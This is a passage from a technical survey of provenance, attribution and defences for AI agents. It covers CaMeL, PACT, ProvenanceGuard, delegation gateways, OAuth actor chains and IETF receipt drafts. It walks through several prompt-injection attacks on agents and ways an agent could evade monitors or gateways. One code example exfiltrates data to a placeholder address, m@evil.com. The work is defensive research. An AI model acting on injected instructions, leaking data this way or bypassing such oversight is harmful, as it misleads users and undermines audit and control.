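If S writes that an email told it to pay V, the auditor has good reason to test that email, but the auditor should not rule out m just because S never mentions it. An attacker can also supply the reason S gives. If m said that company policy required immediate payment, S might repeat this as its own conclusion. The auditor can treat a stated reason as a hypothesis and test it. If S cites the overdue invoice, for example, the auditor can remove the invoice and run the step again.

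### Exact provenance over a model's judgments

Semiring provenance can still be exact when a model makes many small judgments and ordinary software combines them. *EVERGREEN* (Lee, Yeom and colleagues, 2026) uses this approach to check claims in summaries of large tables. One such claim is that every McDonald's location in a set of reviews has multiple complaints about poor service. A model translates the claim into a query, and a model then judges whether each review complains about service. The software counts the complaints at each location and checks that every count is at least two.

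Each judgment has a pair of tokens, one for "this review complains" and one for "this review does not", following Grädel and Tannen's method for negation. If the claim is true, the provenance is a product with two complaints from each of the 62 locations, which gives a reader 124 reviews to check. If the claim is false, the provenance lists the judgments for the first location with fewer than two complaints.

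Evergreen stops as soon as it can settle a claim, so it returns one term instead of the whole polynomial. For the claim "some email asks S to pay V", the full polynomial would be m + n, but Evergreen would return only the email it judged first. That email is enough to justify the claim, but the result leaves out the other email that would also justify it. For some claims, Evergreen judges only a random sample of rows, so its citations cover only that sample.

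Lee and colleagues tested the system on 32 claims about restaurant reviews and customer-support conversations, half of them unsupported. With Claude Opus 4.6, the system detected unsupported claims with an F1 score of 0.94, where 1 would mean it caught them all without false alarms. Checking a claim cost $5.05 on average, compared with $15.88 when the system judged every row. A cheaper model, Qwen3-VL, scored 0.87 at 18 cents per claim.

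The citations were correct 94% of the time with Opus and 82% with the smaller Claude Haiku 4.5. The reference judgments came from a majority vote of three strong models, and one of the researchers agreed with 98.1% of a sample of 104 judgments. Lee and colleagues attribute the system's errors to wrong judgments about individual rows, not to how the software combined them.

A token here records the model's judgment but not the reason for it. If a person checking the evidence finds that a review was sarcastic and contained no complaint, they can set its token to 0 to see whether the remaining cited evidence still supports the claim. This does not show which words in the review caused the model's error.

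Evergreen checks claims and does not explain agents' actions, but a company could organise some decisions in the same way. Suppose a model judges separately whether each of two delivery notes confirms that V's goods arrived, and whether an email disputes the invoice. The tokens r and s stand for the two confirmations, u for a dispute and ū for no dispute. A fixed rule triggers a payment request if either note confirms delivery and the email raises no dispute. The request's label is then (r + s) · ū, which shows exactly how the judgments led to it. The company would still have to estimate how the text of each document influenced the judgment about it.

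## Agent designs that keep data flow explicit

Some agent designs extend Evergreen's approach from checking claims to taking actions. They move steps out of the model and into a database query or a program, whose rules determine what each result depends on.

### Rules about where a row comes from

*Data Flow Control* deals with agents that write database queries. Its main example is an agent that prepares tax returns by copying business expenses from a table of receipts to a table of expenses. A query can do what the user asked and still break a rule. It might reveal one user's receipts in a report, list a Porsche that nobody bought as an expense, or deduct the full cost of a steak dinner when US law allows only half.

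A policy here is a test on the provenance of each row that a query produces. The test can't depend on how the database happens to write the polynomial. Suppose a query adds up the costs of a trip, t, with two receipts, r and s. The database can match the trip with each receipt before adding, or add the receipts first:

```
tr + ts       four tokens
t · (r + s)   three tokens
```

The two expressions are equal, but a rule that allowed at most three tokens would accept only the second, and the policy writer can't know which plan the database will choose. Policies therefore apply to the list of monomials (the separate terms of the multiplied-out polynomial), which is tr and ts for both plans.

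The following policy requires every expense to come from a receipt:

```
SOURCE REQUIRED Receipts SINK Expenses
CONSTRAINT Receipts.id = Expenses.id
ON FAIL KILL
```

Whenever a query writes to the expenses table, each new row must have a receipt in its provenance and carry that receipt's number, or the database cancels the query. If the agent made up the Porsche and wrote it directly into the query, the row would have no receipt in its provenance and the query would fail.

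Suppose the agent submits receipt 3, for a restaurant meal, and claims more than half of the cost. The row's only monomial is r₃. The row passes the rule above because the receipt exists and the numbers match. A privacy rule requires results to combine receipts from at least two users, but it exempts administrators, including the agent. The row fails the tax rule, so the database leaves it out. In the example, a function predicts the business share of each cost. The tax rule caps this share but can't check whether it is accurate, so a family dinner entered as 40% business would pass.

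An agent might try to get around the privacy rule by adding a redundant condition, like the one that put Bob's grant in the provenance of an unrelated payment in the earlier example. It could match each receipt with another user's, so that two users appear in every monomial. The policy language prevents this by testing each use of the receipts table separately. The use that supplies the displayed receipt still involves only one user, so the row fails.

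Policies can also call a language model, for example to decide whether an untidy category label means "meal". The sample policy for this has its test reversed. It accepts any business share if the model classifies the receipt as a meal, so it would accept the full steak dinner. The database would enforce the policy as written, including this mistake.

### Checking provenance without storing it

*Data Flow Control* reports that ordinary provenance capture causes slowdowns ranging from 20% to 10,000-fold. One common method repeats each output row once for every derivation, so a single total over a million receipts becomes a million rows.

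Passant, the program that enforces the policies, rewrites each query to calculate only what the policy needs. Suppose a policy allows a trip total only if no receipt exceeds 100 dollars, and the trip has receipts for 30 and 40 dollars. While the database adds up the costs, an extra column keeps track of the largest one. The database checks that 40 is within the limit and then drops the column. This method relies on the evaluation theorem of Green and colleagues. Some calculations, such as the largest sum of two values from different tables, don't split up this way and need a slower method.

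The tests ran the monotone queries from TPC-H, a standard set of business queries, on DuckDB, Umbra, PostgreSQL, DataFusion and SQL Server. With one simple policy that no row violated, the average overhead was about zero on all five systems. In a more detailed test on DuckDB, the overhead stayed below 10% for all but one query, where Passant had to use a full join instead of a quick check for a matching row. The method that repeats rows slowed some of these queries by 2,000% to 75,000%.

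Passant's advantage over a language model was mostly speed. In one test, 1,000 updates moved records between stages, and 30% broke the required order. Passant and GPT-5.2 both judged every update correctly, but Passant was about 100 times faster. Models did worse when they had to check query results against up to 32 policies about averages and similar statistics, but they saw only the query and the first 100 rows of its result, which is often too little to calculate an average.

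Passant handles only single, monotone queries. It couldn't enforce the company's payment policy, because the delegation rule is recursive and the rule about compliance holds uses negation. It also doesn't follow data from one query to the next. If the agent reads a receipt with one query and types the details into another, the second query's provenance doesn't include the receipt. The receipt rule would then reject a genuine expense, and the privacy rule wouldn't apply, because the second query doesn't read the receipts table. The paper leaves policies for an agent's whole course of action to later work.

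### Writing the program before reading the data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues introduced at Google DeepMind in 2025, tracks values through a whole task. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes how it works. A planning model sees the user's request but none of the emails or web pages involved, and it writes a short program in a restricted form of Python. An interpreter runs the program. To read untrusted text, the program calls a second model, which has no tools and can only return a value. The interpreter labels every value with its sources and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs the company's policies, which are functions that inspect the arguments and their labels.

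Suppose Alice asks S to pay V's latest invoice, and the inbox contains both the invoice, x, and the email with hidden instructions, m. The planning model might write:

```
emails  = search_inbox("supplier V")
amount  = reading_model("How much is V's latest invoice?", emails)
account = supplier_register("V")
pay(account, amount)
```

An auditor can now trace each part of the payment separately:

| Part of the payment | What it depends on |
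|---|---|
| The decision to call `pay` | Alice's request |
| The account number | Alice's request and the supplier register |
| The amount | Alice's request, x and m |

The email m can't add a payment or redirect this one. If Alice had asked only for a summary of her inbox, the program would have contained no call to `pay`, so m couldn't have caused a payment. With an ordinary agent, the auditor would have to estimate this by rerunning the model.

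The amount still depends on a model's judgment. The reading model saw both emails, so the label lists both as possible influences. If m claimed that the invoice was for 4,000 dollars, Alice's 500-dollar limit would stop the payment, but it wouldn't stop a change from 400 to 490 dollars. The program is also a model's interpretation of Alice's request. No email influenced that interpretation, but it could still be wrong.

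Nikolaou and colleagues give an example policy that blocks any payment whose recipient or amount comes from untrusted text. The program above would fail under that policy because the amount comes from an email. Their extension to CaMeL can detect such problems before the program runs and prompt the planning model for a new plan, which could include asking Alice to confirm the amount.

A fixed program protects less when it tells the agent to follow a document. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to read a text file and pay as the file instructs, and the attacker replaces the file's contents. This attack was one of only two that succeeded in CaMeL's own evaluation, and it falls outside CaMeL's stated threat model. An auditor could still use the interpreter's labels to trace the payment details to the file.

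Attackers can also choose which of the program's existing branches runs. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapts CaMeL for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. The planning model has to include steps for whatever might appear, such as a cookie notice to dismiss. An attacker can put a fake cookie notice in an advertisement, and the program's step for dismissing notices then clicks on it.

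### Dependencies that the interpreter misses

CaMeL's labels are only useful to an auditor if they are complete. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found gaps in them. One of their examples works roughly like this:

```
rich = True
tmp  = True
if balance > threshold:  tmp = False
if tmp:                  rich = False
if rich:                 send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
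```

If the balance is above the threshold, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the line that would set `rich` to false. CaMeL changes a variable's label only when the program assigns it a value, so `rich` keeps a public label even though it now reveals something about the balance. The email goes out with no sign that it depends on private data. The label omits this dependency because it comes from an assignment that did not happen. The payment policy similarly needed the token h̄ to record the absence of a hold.

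Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL treats untrusted text as trusted once a program inserts it into a longer string. A message that quoted m could therefore lose its link to m.

Their alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language for agents with a computer-checked proof that its labels prevent such leaks. A program can override the rules by "endorsing" an untrusted value, such as the payment details on a friend's website, so that the agent can send the friend money. The planning model chooses what to endorse before reading any outside text, and an auditor can find each endorsement in the program. An agent built in LLMbda resisted the attacks in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks. Both failures were on the task of making a payment according to instructions in a file.

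Another way to close such gaps is to check the program before it runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) does this with the type system of the programming language Scala. A function that processes classified data won't compile if it could also print, write files or use the network.

### Passing data to a sub-agent

CaMeL's protection can fail when one agent hands work to another. Suppose A's program summarises some emails, including m, and sends S the message "Pay V as described here", followed by the summary. Inside A's program, the summary has a label that includes m, but S treats the whole message as its user's request. S's planning model therefore reads the instruction hidden in m and may write an extra payment into S's program.

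Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, produced this failure with three agents that each ran CaMeL. The user asked for a summary of job applicants' details to be sent to a colleague on Slack. A malicious instruction in the database didn't change the first two agents' programs, but it made the third agent's program also email the details to an outside address.

Their solution is to send instructions and data separately. A's message to S can't contain anything that depends on a tool's output. A has to put such values in named variables, which S's program can use but S's planning model can't read. The variables keep their labels, so m stays in the record when the amount reaches S. Without this separation, A's message wouldn't show where its contents came from, much as the finance department's new certificate didn't show Alice's grant.

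The researchers tested five models on 949 attacked cases each. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and none with the new protocol. Without CaMeL, two older models, GPT-4.1 and Gemini 2.5 Pro, accounted for most of the successful attacks, and no attack succeeded against GPT-5.5.

### Rules for each argument

A web page can be a proper source for one part of an action and not for another. If a user asks an agent to summarise a page and email the summary to their boss, the page should determine the text of the email but not the recipient. Fan, Li and colleagues (2026), in *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*, prove that in such cases a monitor with one rule for the whole tool call will either block some harmless emails or allow some attacks.

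They describe CaMeL as making this kind of whole-call decision, but its policies receive each argument's label, so a company can write separate rules for the recipient and the text. PACT, which Fan and colleagues built, makes separate rules the default. It assigns each argument a role, such as "target" for a recipient or account, "command" for code, or "content" for message text, and each role has a minimum level of trust.

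PACT also labels each value with its sources and a trust level. When the agent combines two values, the result takes all the sources of both and the lower of the two trust levels:

```
supplier register, medium trust  +  email m, low trust
    →  {supplier register, email m}, low trust
```

In semiring terms, PACT has multiplication but no addition. Its labels can show that an account number depends on the register and m, but not that either source would have been enough.

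In the supplier payment, the account number is a target, so m can't supply it. However, PACT wouldn't necessarily stop m from prompting S to pay V with the correct account number. Fan and colleagues exclude attacks in which a model chooses a harmful tool call but fills it with trusted values. Unlike CaMeL, PACT lets the model read outside text before it decides what to do, so tracing the decision's origin still requires working out what influenced the model.

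PACT made no mistakes in 17 test scenarios when given correct labels, which mainly confirms that its rules work as intended. In a controlled test without source tracking across steps, its security score fell from 100% to 80%, because untrusted text could lose its label by passing through another tool.

In ordinary use, PACT has to infer labels by matching text, applying rules and querying a model about unclear cases. On 20 real tools, it assigned the correct role 87.1% of the time and the correct provenance 77.4% of the time. When the label is uncertain, PACT assigns the less trusted one, which is sensible for security but can give an auditor the wrong source. CaMeL gets its labels from running the program, so it doesn't need to infer them outside the gaps that Garby and colleagues found.

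### Finding evidence for an action

An agent can also do the wrong thing without any attacker, simply by misunderstanding its user. She, Liang and Kang (2026), in *Safeguarding LLM Agents from Misalignment through Provenance Analysis*, present a program called ProvenanceGuard that looks for evidence to support each proposed action. It searches the user's request, the descriptions of the tools and the results of earlier steps, and it makes three checks:

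- **Tool:** The tool must serve the user's request. If the user asked to request 30 dollars from Daniel, a tool that sends Daniel money fails.
- **Arguments:** Each value that should come from the context must have a source there. A payment of 300 dollars fails if the user said 30, but a rent payment of 1,700 dollars passes if the user owes two months at 850. Text that the agent is supposed to compose, such as the body of an email, is exempt.
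- **Interpretation:** The context must support only one action. If the user says "handle it" about a payment request, the agent could pay or decline, so it has to ask.

A language model makes most of these judgments, including whether a value follows from its supposed source. For the third check, the model doesn't see the proposed action, so that it can't make up a reason for that action.

The resulting links are arguments that an action is justified, not records of how the agent arrived at it. Any earlier tool result can count as evidence, so an account number from m would have a source in the context. The checks are designed for honest mistakes and don't address prompt injection.

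Across 11 models, ProvenanceGuard missed 2.1% of the misaligned cases on one benchmark, while a model that judged each action directly missed 44.3%. A single prompt with ProvenanceGuard's questions missed 14.7%, so most of the improvement came from asking about provenance at all. That benchmark had only 34 cases in which the agent acted properly, too few to give much evidence about false alarms. On a second benchmark, ProvenanceGuard missed 18.7% of the misaligned cases and direct judgment missed 32.4%. ProvenanceGuard also interrupted 13.0% of the tasks that the agent was completing successfully, while direct judgment interrupted 31.2%.

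### What the restrictions cost

Three groups have rerun CaMeL on AgentDojo. Garby and colleagues used the 16 banking tasks and ran each three times. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a rival defence, used all 97 tasks, as did Fan and colleagues. The table shows the share of tasks completed when nobody was attacking the agent:

| Test | Comparison | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Banking tasks, two models | 67% and 71% with CaMeL's policy checks off | 37.5% for both |
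| All tasks, *SecureClaw*'s test | 61% with SecureClaw | 30% |
| All tasks, five models | 21% to 61% with no defence | 11% to 31% |

No attack succeeded in the CaMeL runs in the last column. In the third test, PACT completed 19% to 46% of the tasks. Its results table also shows no successful attacks, although the text gives a security score of 96.3% for two of the five models. All three groups were promoting their own alternatives to CaMeL, and a different setup might have given CaMeL better scores, but they agree that it fails many tasks that other agents complete.

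Part of the loss comes from planning without seeing the data. Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include one of CaMeL's designers, measured this on 112 multi-step professional tasks by running CaMeL with no policies. Success fell by an average of 21.6 percentage points across five models, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Sending instructions and data separately lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for those two models. The loss may shrink as models get better at writing programs for data they haven't seen. It is larger when the plan has to cover many possibilities. Foerster and colleagues' design for agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen retained at most 57% of the performance of leading models.

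The policy checks cause a separate loss. In the banking tests, turning them on reduced completed runs from 32 to 18 out of 48 with one model, and from 34 to 18 with the other. This matters less to a company that mainly wants a record, because the interpreter can track where values come from without blocking every action that uses an untrusted one. The company could enforce only a few rules, such as requiring account numbers to come from the supplier register. It would still have to accept the loss from planning in advance, because planning in advance rules out m as the reason for the payment.

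This tradeoff is probably a good one for supplier payments, because the steps are few and predictable, a mistake can cost money, and an auditor is likely to ask where the account number came from. Open-ended research is a worse fit because the agent often can't know what to do next until it has read something. A company could let an ordinary agent do the reading, without permission to pay anyone, and send payments through a program written from Alice's request.

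## Recording which grant an action used

If agent A pays a supplier, the bank's log shows the payment, and CaMeL's labels can trace the account number to the supplier register, but neither record identifies the grant A acted under. A company that keeps old versions of its grants and rules can later work out which grants would have permitted the payment, but not which of them A used. Its systems therefore have to record the grant used when the payment happens.

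### Two tasks in one log

Suppose Alice and Bob each give A a task on the same morning. One asks A to pay supplier V, and the other asks it to pay a second approved supplier, W. The log reads as follows, with a trace number that links connected calls:

```
10:01   A reads V's invoice       trace 1
10:02   A reads W's invoice       trace 2
10:03   A pays V 400 dollars      trace 1
10:04   A pays W 250 dollars      trace 2
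```

The log would be identical whether Alice asked for the payment to V and Bob for the payment to W, or the other way round. The trace numbers show which invoice goes with which payment, but not who set each task. The polynomials don't distinguish these cases either, because each payment has one derivation from Alice's grant and another from Bob's. If the company later learned that someone had stolen Alice's password that morning, it wouldn't know which payment to investigate. With ten such pairs of tasks, there would be 2¹⁰ = 1,024 possible assignments of tasks to people.

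Mishra and Sharad proved this ambiguity for logs that leave out the delegation. The terms of the grants can sometimes resolve it. For example, if Alice's limit were 300 dollars, only Bob's grant could have permitted the payment to V. Alice's original message would also help if the company had kept it.

Mishra and Sharad simulated three kinds of workflow to see how badly reconstruction can fail. When agents read from several tools in parallel, grouping events by trace recovered a median of 6% of a delegation's events, and a typical delegation was split into 35 unconnected groups of events. When agents often retried failed steps, the median was 4% and a typical delegation was split into 55 groups. In the third workflow, which used several agents, the median was 100%, but only because the simulator kept each delegation in one trace. The percentages therefore depend on the simulator's settings.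 Results for the two other reconstruction methods are hard to interpret because the paper's text and table assign some of the same figures to different methods.

### Attaching the delegation at a gateway

Their solution is a gateway, which is software between the agent and its tools. It does four things:

1. It creates an identifier for each delegation and ties it to a user who has logged in.
2. It attaches the identifier to every tool call under that delegation. A sub-agent's delegation has its own identifier and a link to its parent.
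3. It translates each tool's operations into a shared vocabulary, such as "read", "write", "share" and "invoke".
4. It writes a record of the call. If the call has no delegation, the record says "unbound" instead of leaving the field empty.

An auditor can then use a single search to find everything A did for Alice, including the work of its sub-agents. In a small test, the gateway increased the average record from 341 to 588 bytes and added less than 0.3 milliseconds to 95% of calls. Mishra and Sharad expect more overhead at production scale.

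The gateway has to determine which delegation each call belongs to. Agent A holds valid delegations from both Alice and Bob, so if the gateway took the delegation from the output of A's model, a prompt injection could make it record the wrong one. It would be safer to run Alice's and Bob's tasks as separate processes with separate credentials, so that the gateway could identify the delegation from the credential.

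Each record can hold one delegation, which is enough to separate Alice's task from Bob's. It has no standard field for the payment amount, the policy version or the other facts in the derivation, such as Carol's approval.

### What the record has to contain

Surapani and colleagues want a person to be able to trace an agent's action to a human, check that it stayed within what the human delegated, and contest it afterwards. They describe a tool call by its chain of principals, operation, target, arguments, permitted scope, time or session, and evidence of provenance. A chain of principals can't show that Alice and Bob are alternatives, so a company that wanted to use the polynomial would need a little more. A record of S's payment might look like this:

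```
action:        S pays V 400 dollars for invoice 118
support used:  a (version 2), c (version 1), d (version 1)
alternative:   b (version 1), c (version 1), d (version 1)
policy:        supplier payments, version 7
checked:       3 December, 10:03:07
paid:          3 December, 10:03:09
```

The grants need version numbers because people edit them. Suppose the limit in Alice's grant a was 300 dollars on Monday and she raised it to 500 on Tuesday. An auditor who looked up the grant on Wednesday would wrongly conclude that it had permitted a 400-dollar payment on Monday. In *Delegation Receipt Protocol for AI Agent Authorization* (Nelson, 2026), a grant's identifier is a hash, which is a short code calculated from the grant's contents. Any edit produces a different identifier, so records made before the edit still refer to the old terms.

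The policy version matters for the same reason. If the company later required signatures from both Alice and Bob, running the new rules on Monday's grants would give abcd instead of acd + bcd.

The "support used" line records the set of grants that the task selected. The company also needs this set when someone revokes a grant. The alternative is less essential, because the company can recalculate it if it keeps the old grants and rules.

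The action line must include the arguments. Without them, a record such as "S used the payment tool under grant a" could describe either a payment of 400 dollars to V or one of 4,000 dollars to somebody else.

Two timestamps are necessary because a permission can end between the check and the payment. The Decentralized Identity Foundation's *Threat Model for Delegated Authority in AI-Mediated Systems* notes that authority may be valid when someone issues it but invalid when an agent uses it. Clocks can be wrong, or an attacker can change them, so Nelson's protocol takes the time from an independent time-stamping service.

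### User and actor fields in OAuth

OAuth is a widely used set of standards for giving software limited access to a service. It includes the token exchange standard by Jones and colleagues, also known as RFC 8693. If Alice's permission reached S through A, a credential issued under that standard might contain:

```
{
  "sub": "alice",
  "act": {
    "sub": "agent_s",
    "act": { "sub": "agent_a" }
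  }
}
```

The outer `sub` (subject) identifies the user, and the outer `act` (actor) identifies the agent making the request. The inner `act` identifies the previous agent. A service may use the current actor to decide whether to allow the request, but it must treat earlier actors as information only.

These fields can't combine several people's grants. Alice's and Bob's grants both support S's payment, but the credential names only the user whose permission S exchanged. If the company required both signatures, the credential would still have only one subject field. Carol is neither the user nor an actor, so her approval doesn't appear. The fields also name people and agents instead of grants, so two grants from Alice with different limits could produce the same names. A company could add its own fields, but other services would have to agree on what they meant.

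Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues (2026) note in *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* that the standard allows nested actors but has no common rules for building, extending or checking even a single chain. They propose such rules, along with an identifier that stays the same throughout a workflow. In the simpler version, the server that issues credentials vouches for the chain. In the stronger version, each agent also signs its own step. An agent joins the chain only when it acts, not when it merely receives a credential. The proposal doesn't define how branches merge, so it can't represent a permission that depends on both Alice and Carol.

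### Draft standards for receipts and chains

The actor-chain proposal is one of several drafts submitted to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which develops internet standards. The drafts cover different parts of the record.

Nelson's protocol records the original grant in a receipt, which the user signs before the agent starts work. The receipt lists the allowed actions, the prohibitions, a time window and a hash of the instructions that the agent's operator plans to give it. It goes into an append-only log. If the operator later changes the instructions, their hash no longer matches the one in the receipt. An earlier version of the draft, from May 2026, requires the log to record, for each action, the receipt's hash, the type of action, a hash of its contents, its destination, the time and the agent's signature.

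This covers much of the record above, but a receipt has only one user's signature and can name only one parent receipt, so it can represent Alice's chain or Bob's, but not that either is enough. Nelson's company, Authproof, offers a hosted version of the protocol, so the company has a commercial interest in the draft.

Two drafts add signatures to OAuth's chain of actors. *OAuth Actor Receipts for Delegation Provenance* (2026) has each issuer sign for the actor it added, so a service doesn't have to rely only on the latest issuer. In a companion draft on actor proofs, each actor signs to confirm that it took part and which service it meant to contact.

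Another draft, on authorization receipts, deals with approvals of single actions. Each approval can be used only once, and whoever initiates an action can't approve it. If Carol's approval of V covered one payment, this protocol could stop S from using it in two separate requests. Such reuse can't be detected from the exponents in a polynomial.

*Cryptographically Verifiable Intent Chain for AI Agent Content Provenance* (Krishnan, Prasad and colleagues, 2026) tracks content instead of permission. Each agent or filter signs a hash of what it received and a hash of what it produced, so if A sends S a harmful instruction, A's operator can't later claim that a filter added it. The credential contains only a summary hash, and the full record stays in a separate log.

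These hashes establish that certain text went in and other text came out, but not why an agent acted, despite the word "intent". The draft also checks that each step's input is exactly the previous step's output. That check works for a message passing through a row of filters, but it doesn't suit an agent like S, whose input combines A's message with an invoice, an email and an entry from the supplier register.

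In *Binding Per-Action Authorization and Memory Provenance into Agent Action Capsules*, Rampalli (2026) proposes one record that links to evidence about what the agent did, whether it had permission and where the information it acted on came from. The record could show that S made a permitted payment after reading a memory entry from an untrusted source. Rampalli warns that a link to a permission doesn't prove that the permission is valid, so an auditor still has to open the link and check.

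All of these are individual drafts. Nelson introduced the receipt protocol to an IETF mailing list as "an individual submission", and none of the drafts has the kind of name that the IETF uses once a working group adopts one. A draft lapses after six months unless its authors update it. This was the position of four of them on 5 December 2026:

| Draft | Latest known version | Expiry |
|---|---|---|
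| Actor chains, Prasad and colleagues | June 2026 | 17 December 2026 |
| Delegation receipts, Nelson | June 2026 | 15 December 2026 |
| Intent chains, Krishnan and colleagues | March 2026 | Expired on 19 September 2026 |
| Combined record, Rampalli | July 2026 | 6 January 2027 |

A company that built on one of these now would have to be prepared for the format to change or disappear.

### W3C PROV and PROV-AGENT

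The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) already has a general standard for provenance, called PROV. It describes entities such as documents, activities such as payments, and the agents responsible for them. A PROV record of S's payment could include:

```
used(payment, grant_a)
used(payment, grant_b)
used(payment, approval_c)
used(payment, delegation_d)
actedOnBehalfOf(agent_s, agent_a)
```

These lines give only the lineage, so they can't distinguish acd + bcd from abcd. Leaving out the line for grant b would correctly show that S relied on Alice but would hide the alternative. PROV's `alternateOf` relation can't record that alternative, because it links two descriptions of the same thing, not two grants that could each support a payment.

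PROV-AGENT, a 2025 extension of PROV for AI workflows, adds types for prompts, model calls and tool runs. An auditor could use it to trace a payment back to the model call that requested it, and from there to the email m and the invoice. The links would record only that the model call used both, not whether either alone would have been enough.

Both formats could store a polynomial as an extra attribute, and PROV's existing software could at least pass it along. Mishra and Sharad similarly suggest that their own records could be a specialised form of PROV, but they think PROV lacks rules for who may create a delegation identifier and for what a missing record means.

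### SentinelAgent

Patil (2026), in *SentinelAgent*, goes further than these formats by combining the record with enforcement. The system is for government work in which agents from different agencies and contractors pass tasks to one another. A central service, which doesn't use a language model to make authorisation decisions, signs every delegation and checks seven properties:

- An agent can't delegate more authority than it has.
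- A subtask doesn't contradict the user's original request.
- Every policy restriction on the original delegation stays in force.
- An auditor can recover the chain of delegations behind any action.
- There is a limit on how much an agent can do after the system detects a violation.
- An agent makes only the calls that its delegation lists.
- An agent produces only the types of output that its delegation allows.

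The fourth property matters most for attribution. Each delegation contains the hash of its parent, so the service can follow the hashes from S to A to Alice in two lookups. Changing an old delegation would break the later links. But each delegation has only one parent, so the search would return Alice's chain, which doesn't include Bob or Carol.

The second property is the only one that depends on a model's judgment, and it is much weaker than the others. An off-the-shelf language classifier caught 1.7% of malicious subtasks. Training it on 190 examples raised the rate to 88.3%, but the intent check missed 20 of 23 requests that attackers had carefully reworded. Patil considers a perfect check impractical for ordinary language.

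On Patil's own benchmark of 516 scenarios, the checks on intent, calls and outputs together caught all 150 attacks and raised no false alarms. A program that explores every state of a formal model found no violation of the other six properties in 2.7 million states. These results show that the design is consistent and handles the attacks Patil thought of. They don't show how it would perform in a real agency, and all the guarantees hold only if nobody has compromised the central service.

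### Forged credentials and missing records

A signature on a record proves that someone had the key. If a thief used Alice's key to sign a grant, every later check would succeed and the record would name Alice. Similarly, if A passes its credential to three sub-agents, the gateway can't identify which of them made a payment.

An agent might also try to attribute its action to someone else's delegation. Mishra and Sharad prevent this by having the gateway create the identifiers itself and treat anything the agent supplies as an unverified hint. The gateway can also raise an alarm if one identifier appears with two different users. That alarm wouldn't catch an agent that switched between two delegations from Alice, because the user would be the same.

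The gateway doesn't help if an agent bypasses it, for example by calling the bank directly with a saved password. Mishra and Sharad suggest comparing the records with a list of the tools an agent is supposed to use, since a tool with no entries could be a sign of evasion. This is weak evidence because the agent may not have needed the tool. The comparison would also miss an agent that sent one payment through the gateway and another around it, since the payment tool would still have an entry. It would be safer for the bank to reject any request that didn't come through the gateway.

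Hash chains make it hard to delete an old entry, because each entry contains the hash of the one before it, but they don't reveal actions that were never logged. To find those, the company needs a second source, such as the bank's list of payments. Any payment on that list without a matching entry in the company's log needs an explanation.

A person can also hide misuse by splitting it across several delegations. In an example from Mishra and Sharad, an employee who wants to leak ten documents creates ten delegations to read one document each, and an eleventh to share the results. No single delegation looks suspicious. An auditor would have to search by employee, which works only if every delegation records the person who authorized it.

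### Keeping the record private

A complete record can reveal more than a service needs. A bank that saw the full chain behind S's payment would learn who can approve suppliers, which employees share an agent and perhaps which companies are working together on a confidential deal. Prasad and colleagues let the server that issues credentials show the whole chain, part of it or only the current actor, while keeping the full version for auditors. But the company can't hide the earlier actors from a service that bases its decision on them.

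Rampalli notes that someone can guess the contents of a hash if there are few possibilities. For example, an outsider with a list of 500 suppliers could hash every whole-dollar payment of up to 500 dollars to each one. One of those 250,000 hashes would match the payment to V. Adding a secret random value before hashing prevents this.

Recording alternatives also creates a privacy problem. Bob's grant appears in the record of S's payment even if S relied on Alice's grant and Bob knew nothing about the payment. The company could keep the "alternative" line in an internal record with tighter access, or leave it out and recalculate it when an auditor has a reason to ask.

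## What the record says about responsibility

The record of S's payment to V lists Alice's grant, Carol's approval and A's delegation as the support the payment used, and Bob's grant as an alternative. Suppose the company later discovers that it owed V nothing. Its managers will ask who is responsible, which could mean any of four things:

| Claim about a grant | Is it true of Alice's grant? | What settles it |
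|---|---|---|
| It was sufficient together with other facts | Yes, with c and d | The polynomial |
| It was necessary | No, because Bob's grant would have done instead | The polynomial |
| Its giver intended the action | No, she wanted A to pay real debts | What Alice wrote and knew |
| Its giver is answerable for the action | Undecided | Laws, contracts and company rules |

Someone who is answerable for an action has to explain it, put it right or accept a penalty for it. "The payment went through on Alice's grant" is true, but it establishes only that her grant was part of a sufficient set, not that she is answerable for the payment. Necessity doesn't settle who is answerable either. If people were answerable only for necessary grants, neither Alice nor Bob would be answerable for letting A pay suppliers, because each could say that the other's grant would have allowed it anyway.

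The record may contain some evidence of intention. In the format that Wei and Xiong propose, Alice's grant states a task, such as settling this month's supplier invoices, and an auditor can compare the payment with that task. But someone who gives an agent permission usually intends a kind of action rather than a particular instance. If the company had owed V the money, the payment would have matched Alice's intention even if she had never heard of V.

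### Causal responsibility

Database researchers have put numbers on how much a result depends on each fact. Meliou, Gatterbauer and colleagues (2010), in *The Complexity of Causality and Responsibility for Query Answers and non-Answers*, adapt definitions of causality by Halpern, Pearl and Chockler. The user first chooses which facts to examine as possible causes, and takes the rest as given. A fact is a counterfactual cause if removing it alone removes the result. It is an actual cause if it becomes a counterfactual cause after the removal of some set of other facts, which Meliou and colleagues call a contingency. A fact's responsibility is

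```
1 / (1 + size of its smallest contingency)
```

or 0 if the fact isn't a cause. For the payment, whose polynomial is acd + bcd, this gives:

```
c and d:   nothing else has to go first    1/(1 + 0)  =  1
a:         b has to go first               1/(1 + 1)  =  1/2
b:         a has to go first               1/(1 + 1)  =  1/2
```

Responsibility gives Alice's and Bob's grants some weight, unlike a test that removes one grant at a time, because each grant would be necessary if the other were already gone. It gives no weight to redundant conditions. Under the badly worded rule that gave a payment the polynomial g² + gh, Bob's unrelated grant h has a responsibility of 0, because the payment doesn't depend on h no matter which other grants are removed.

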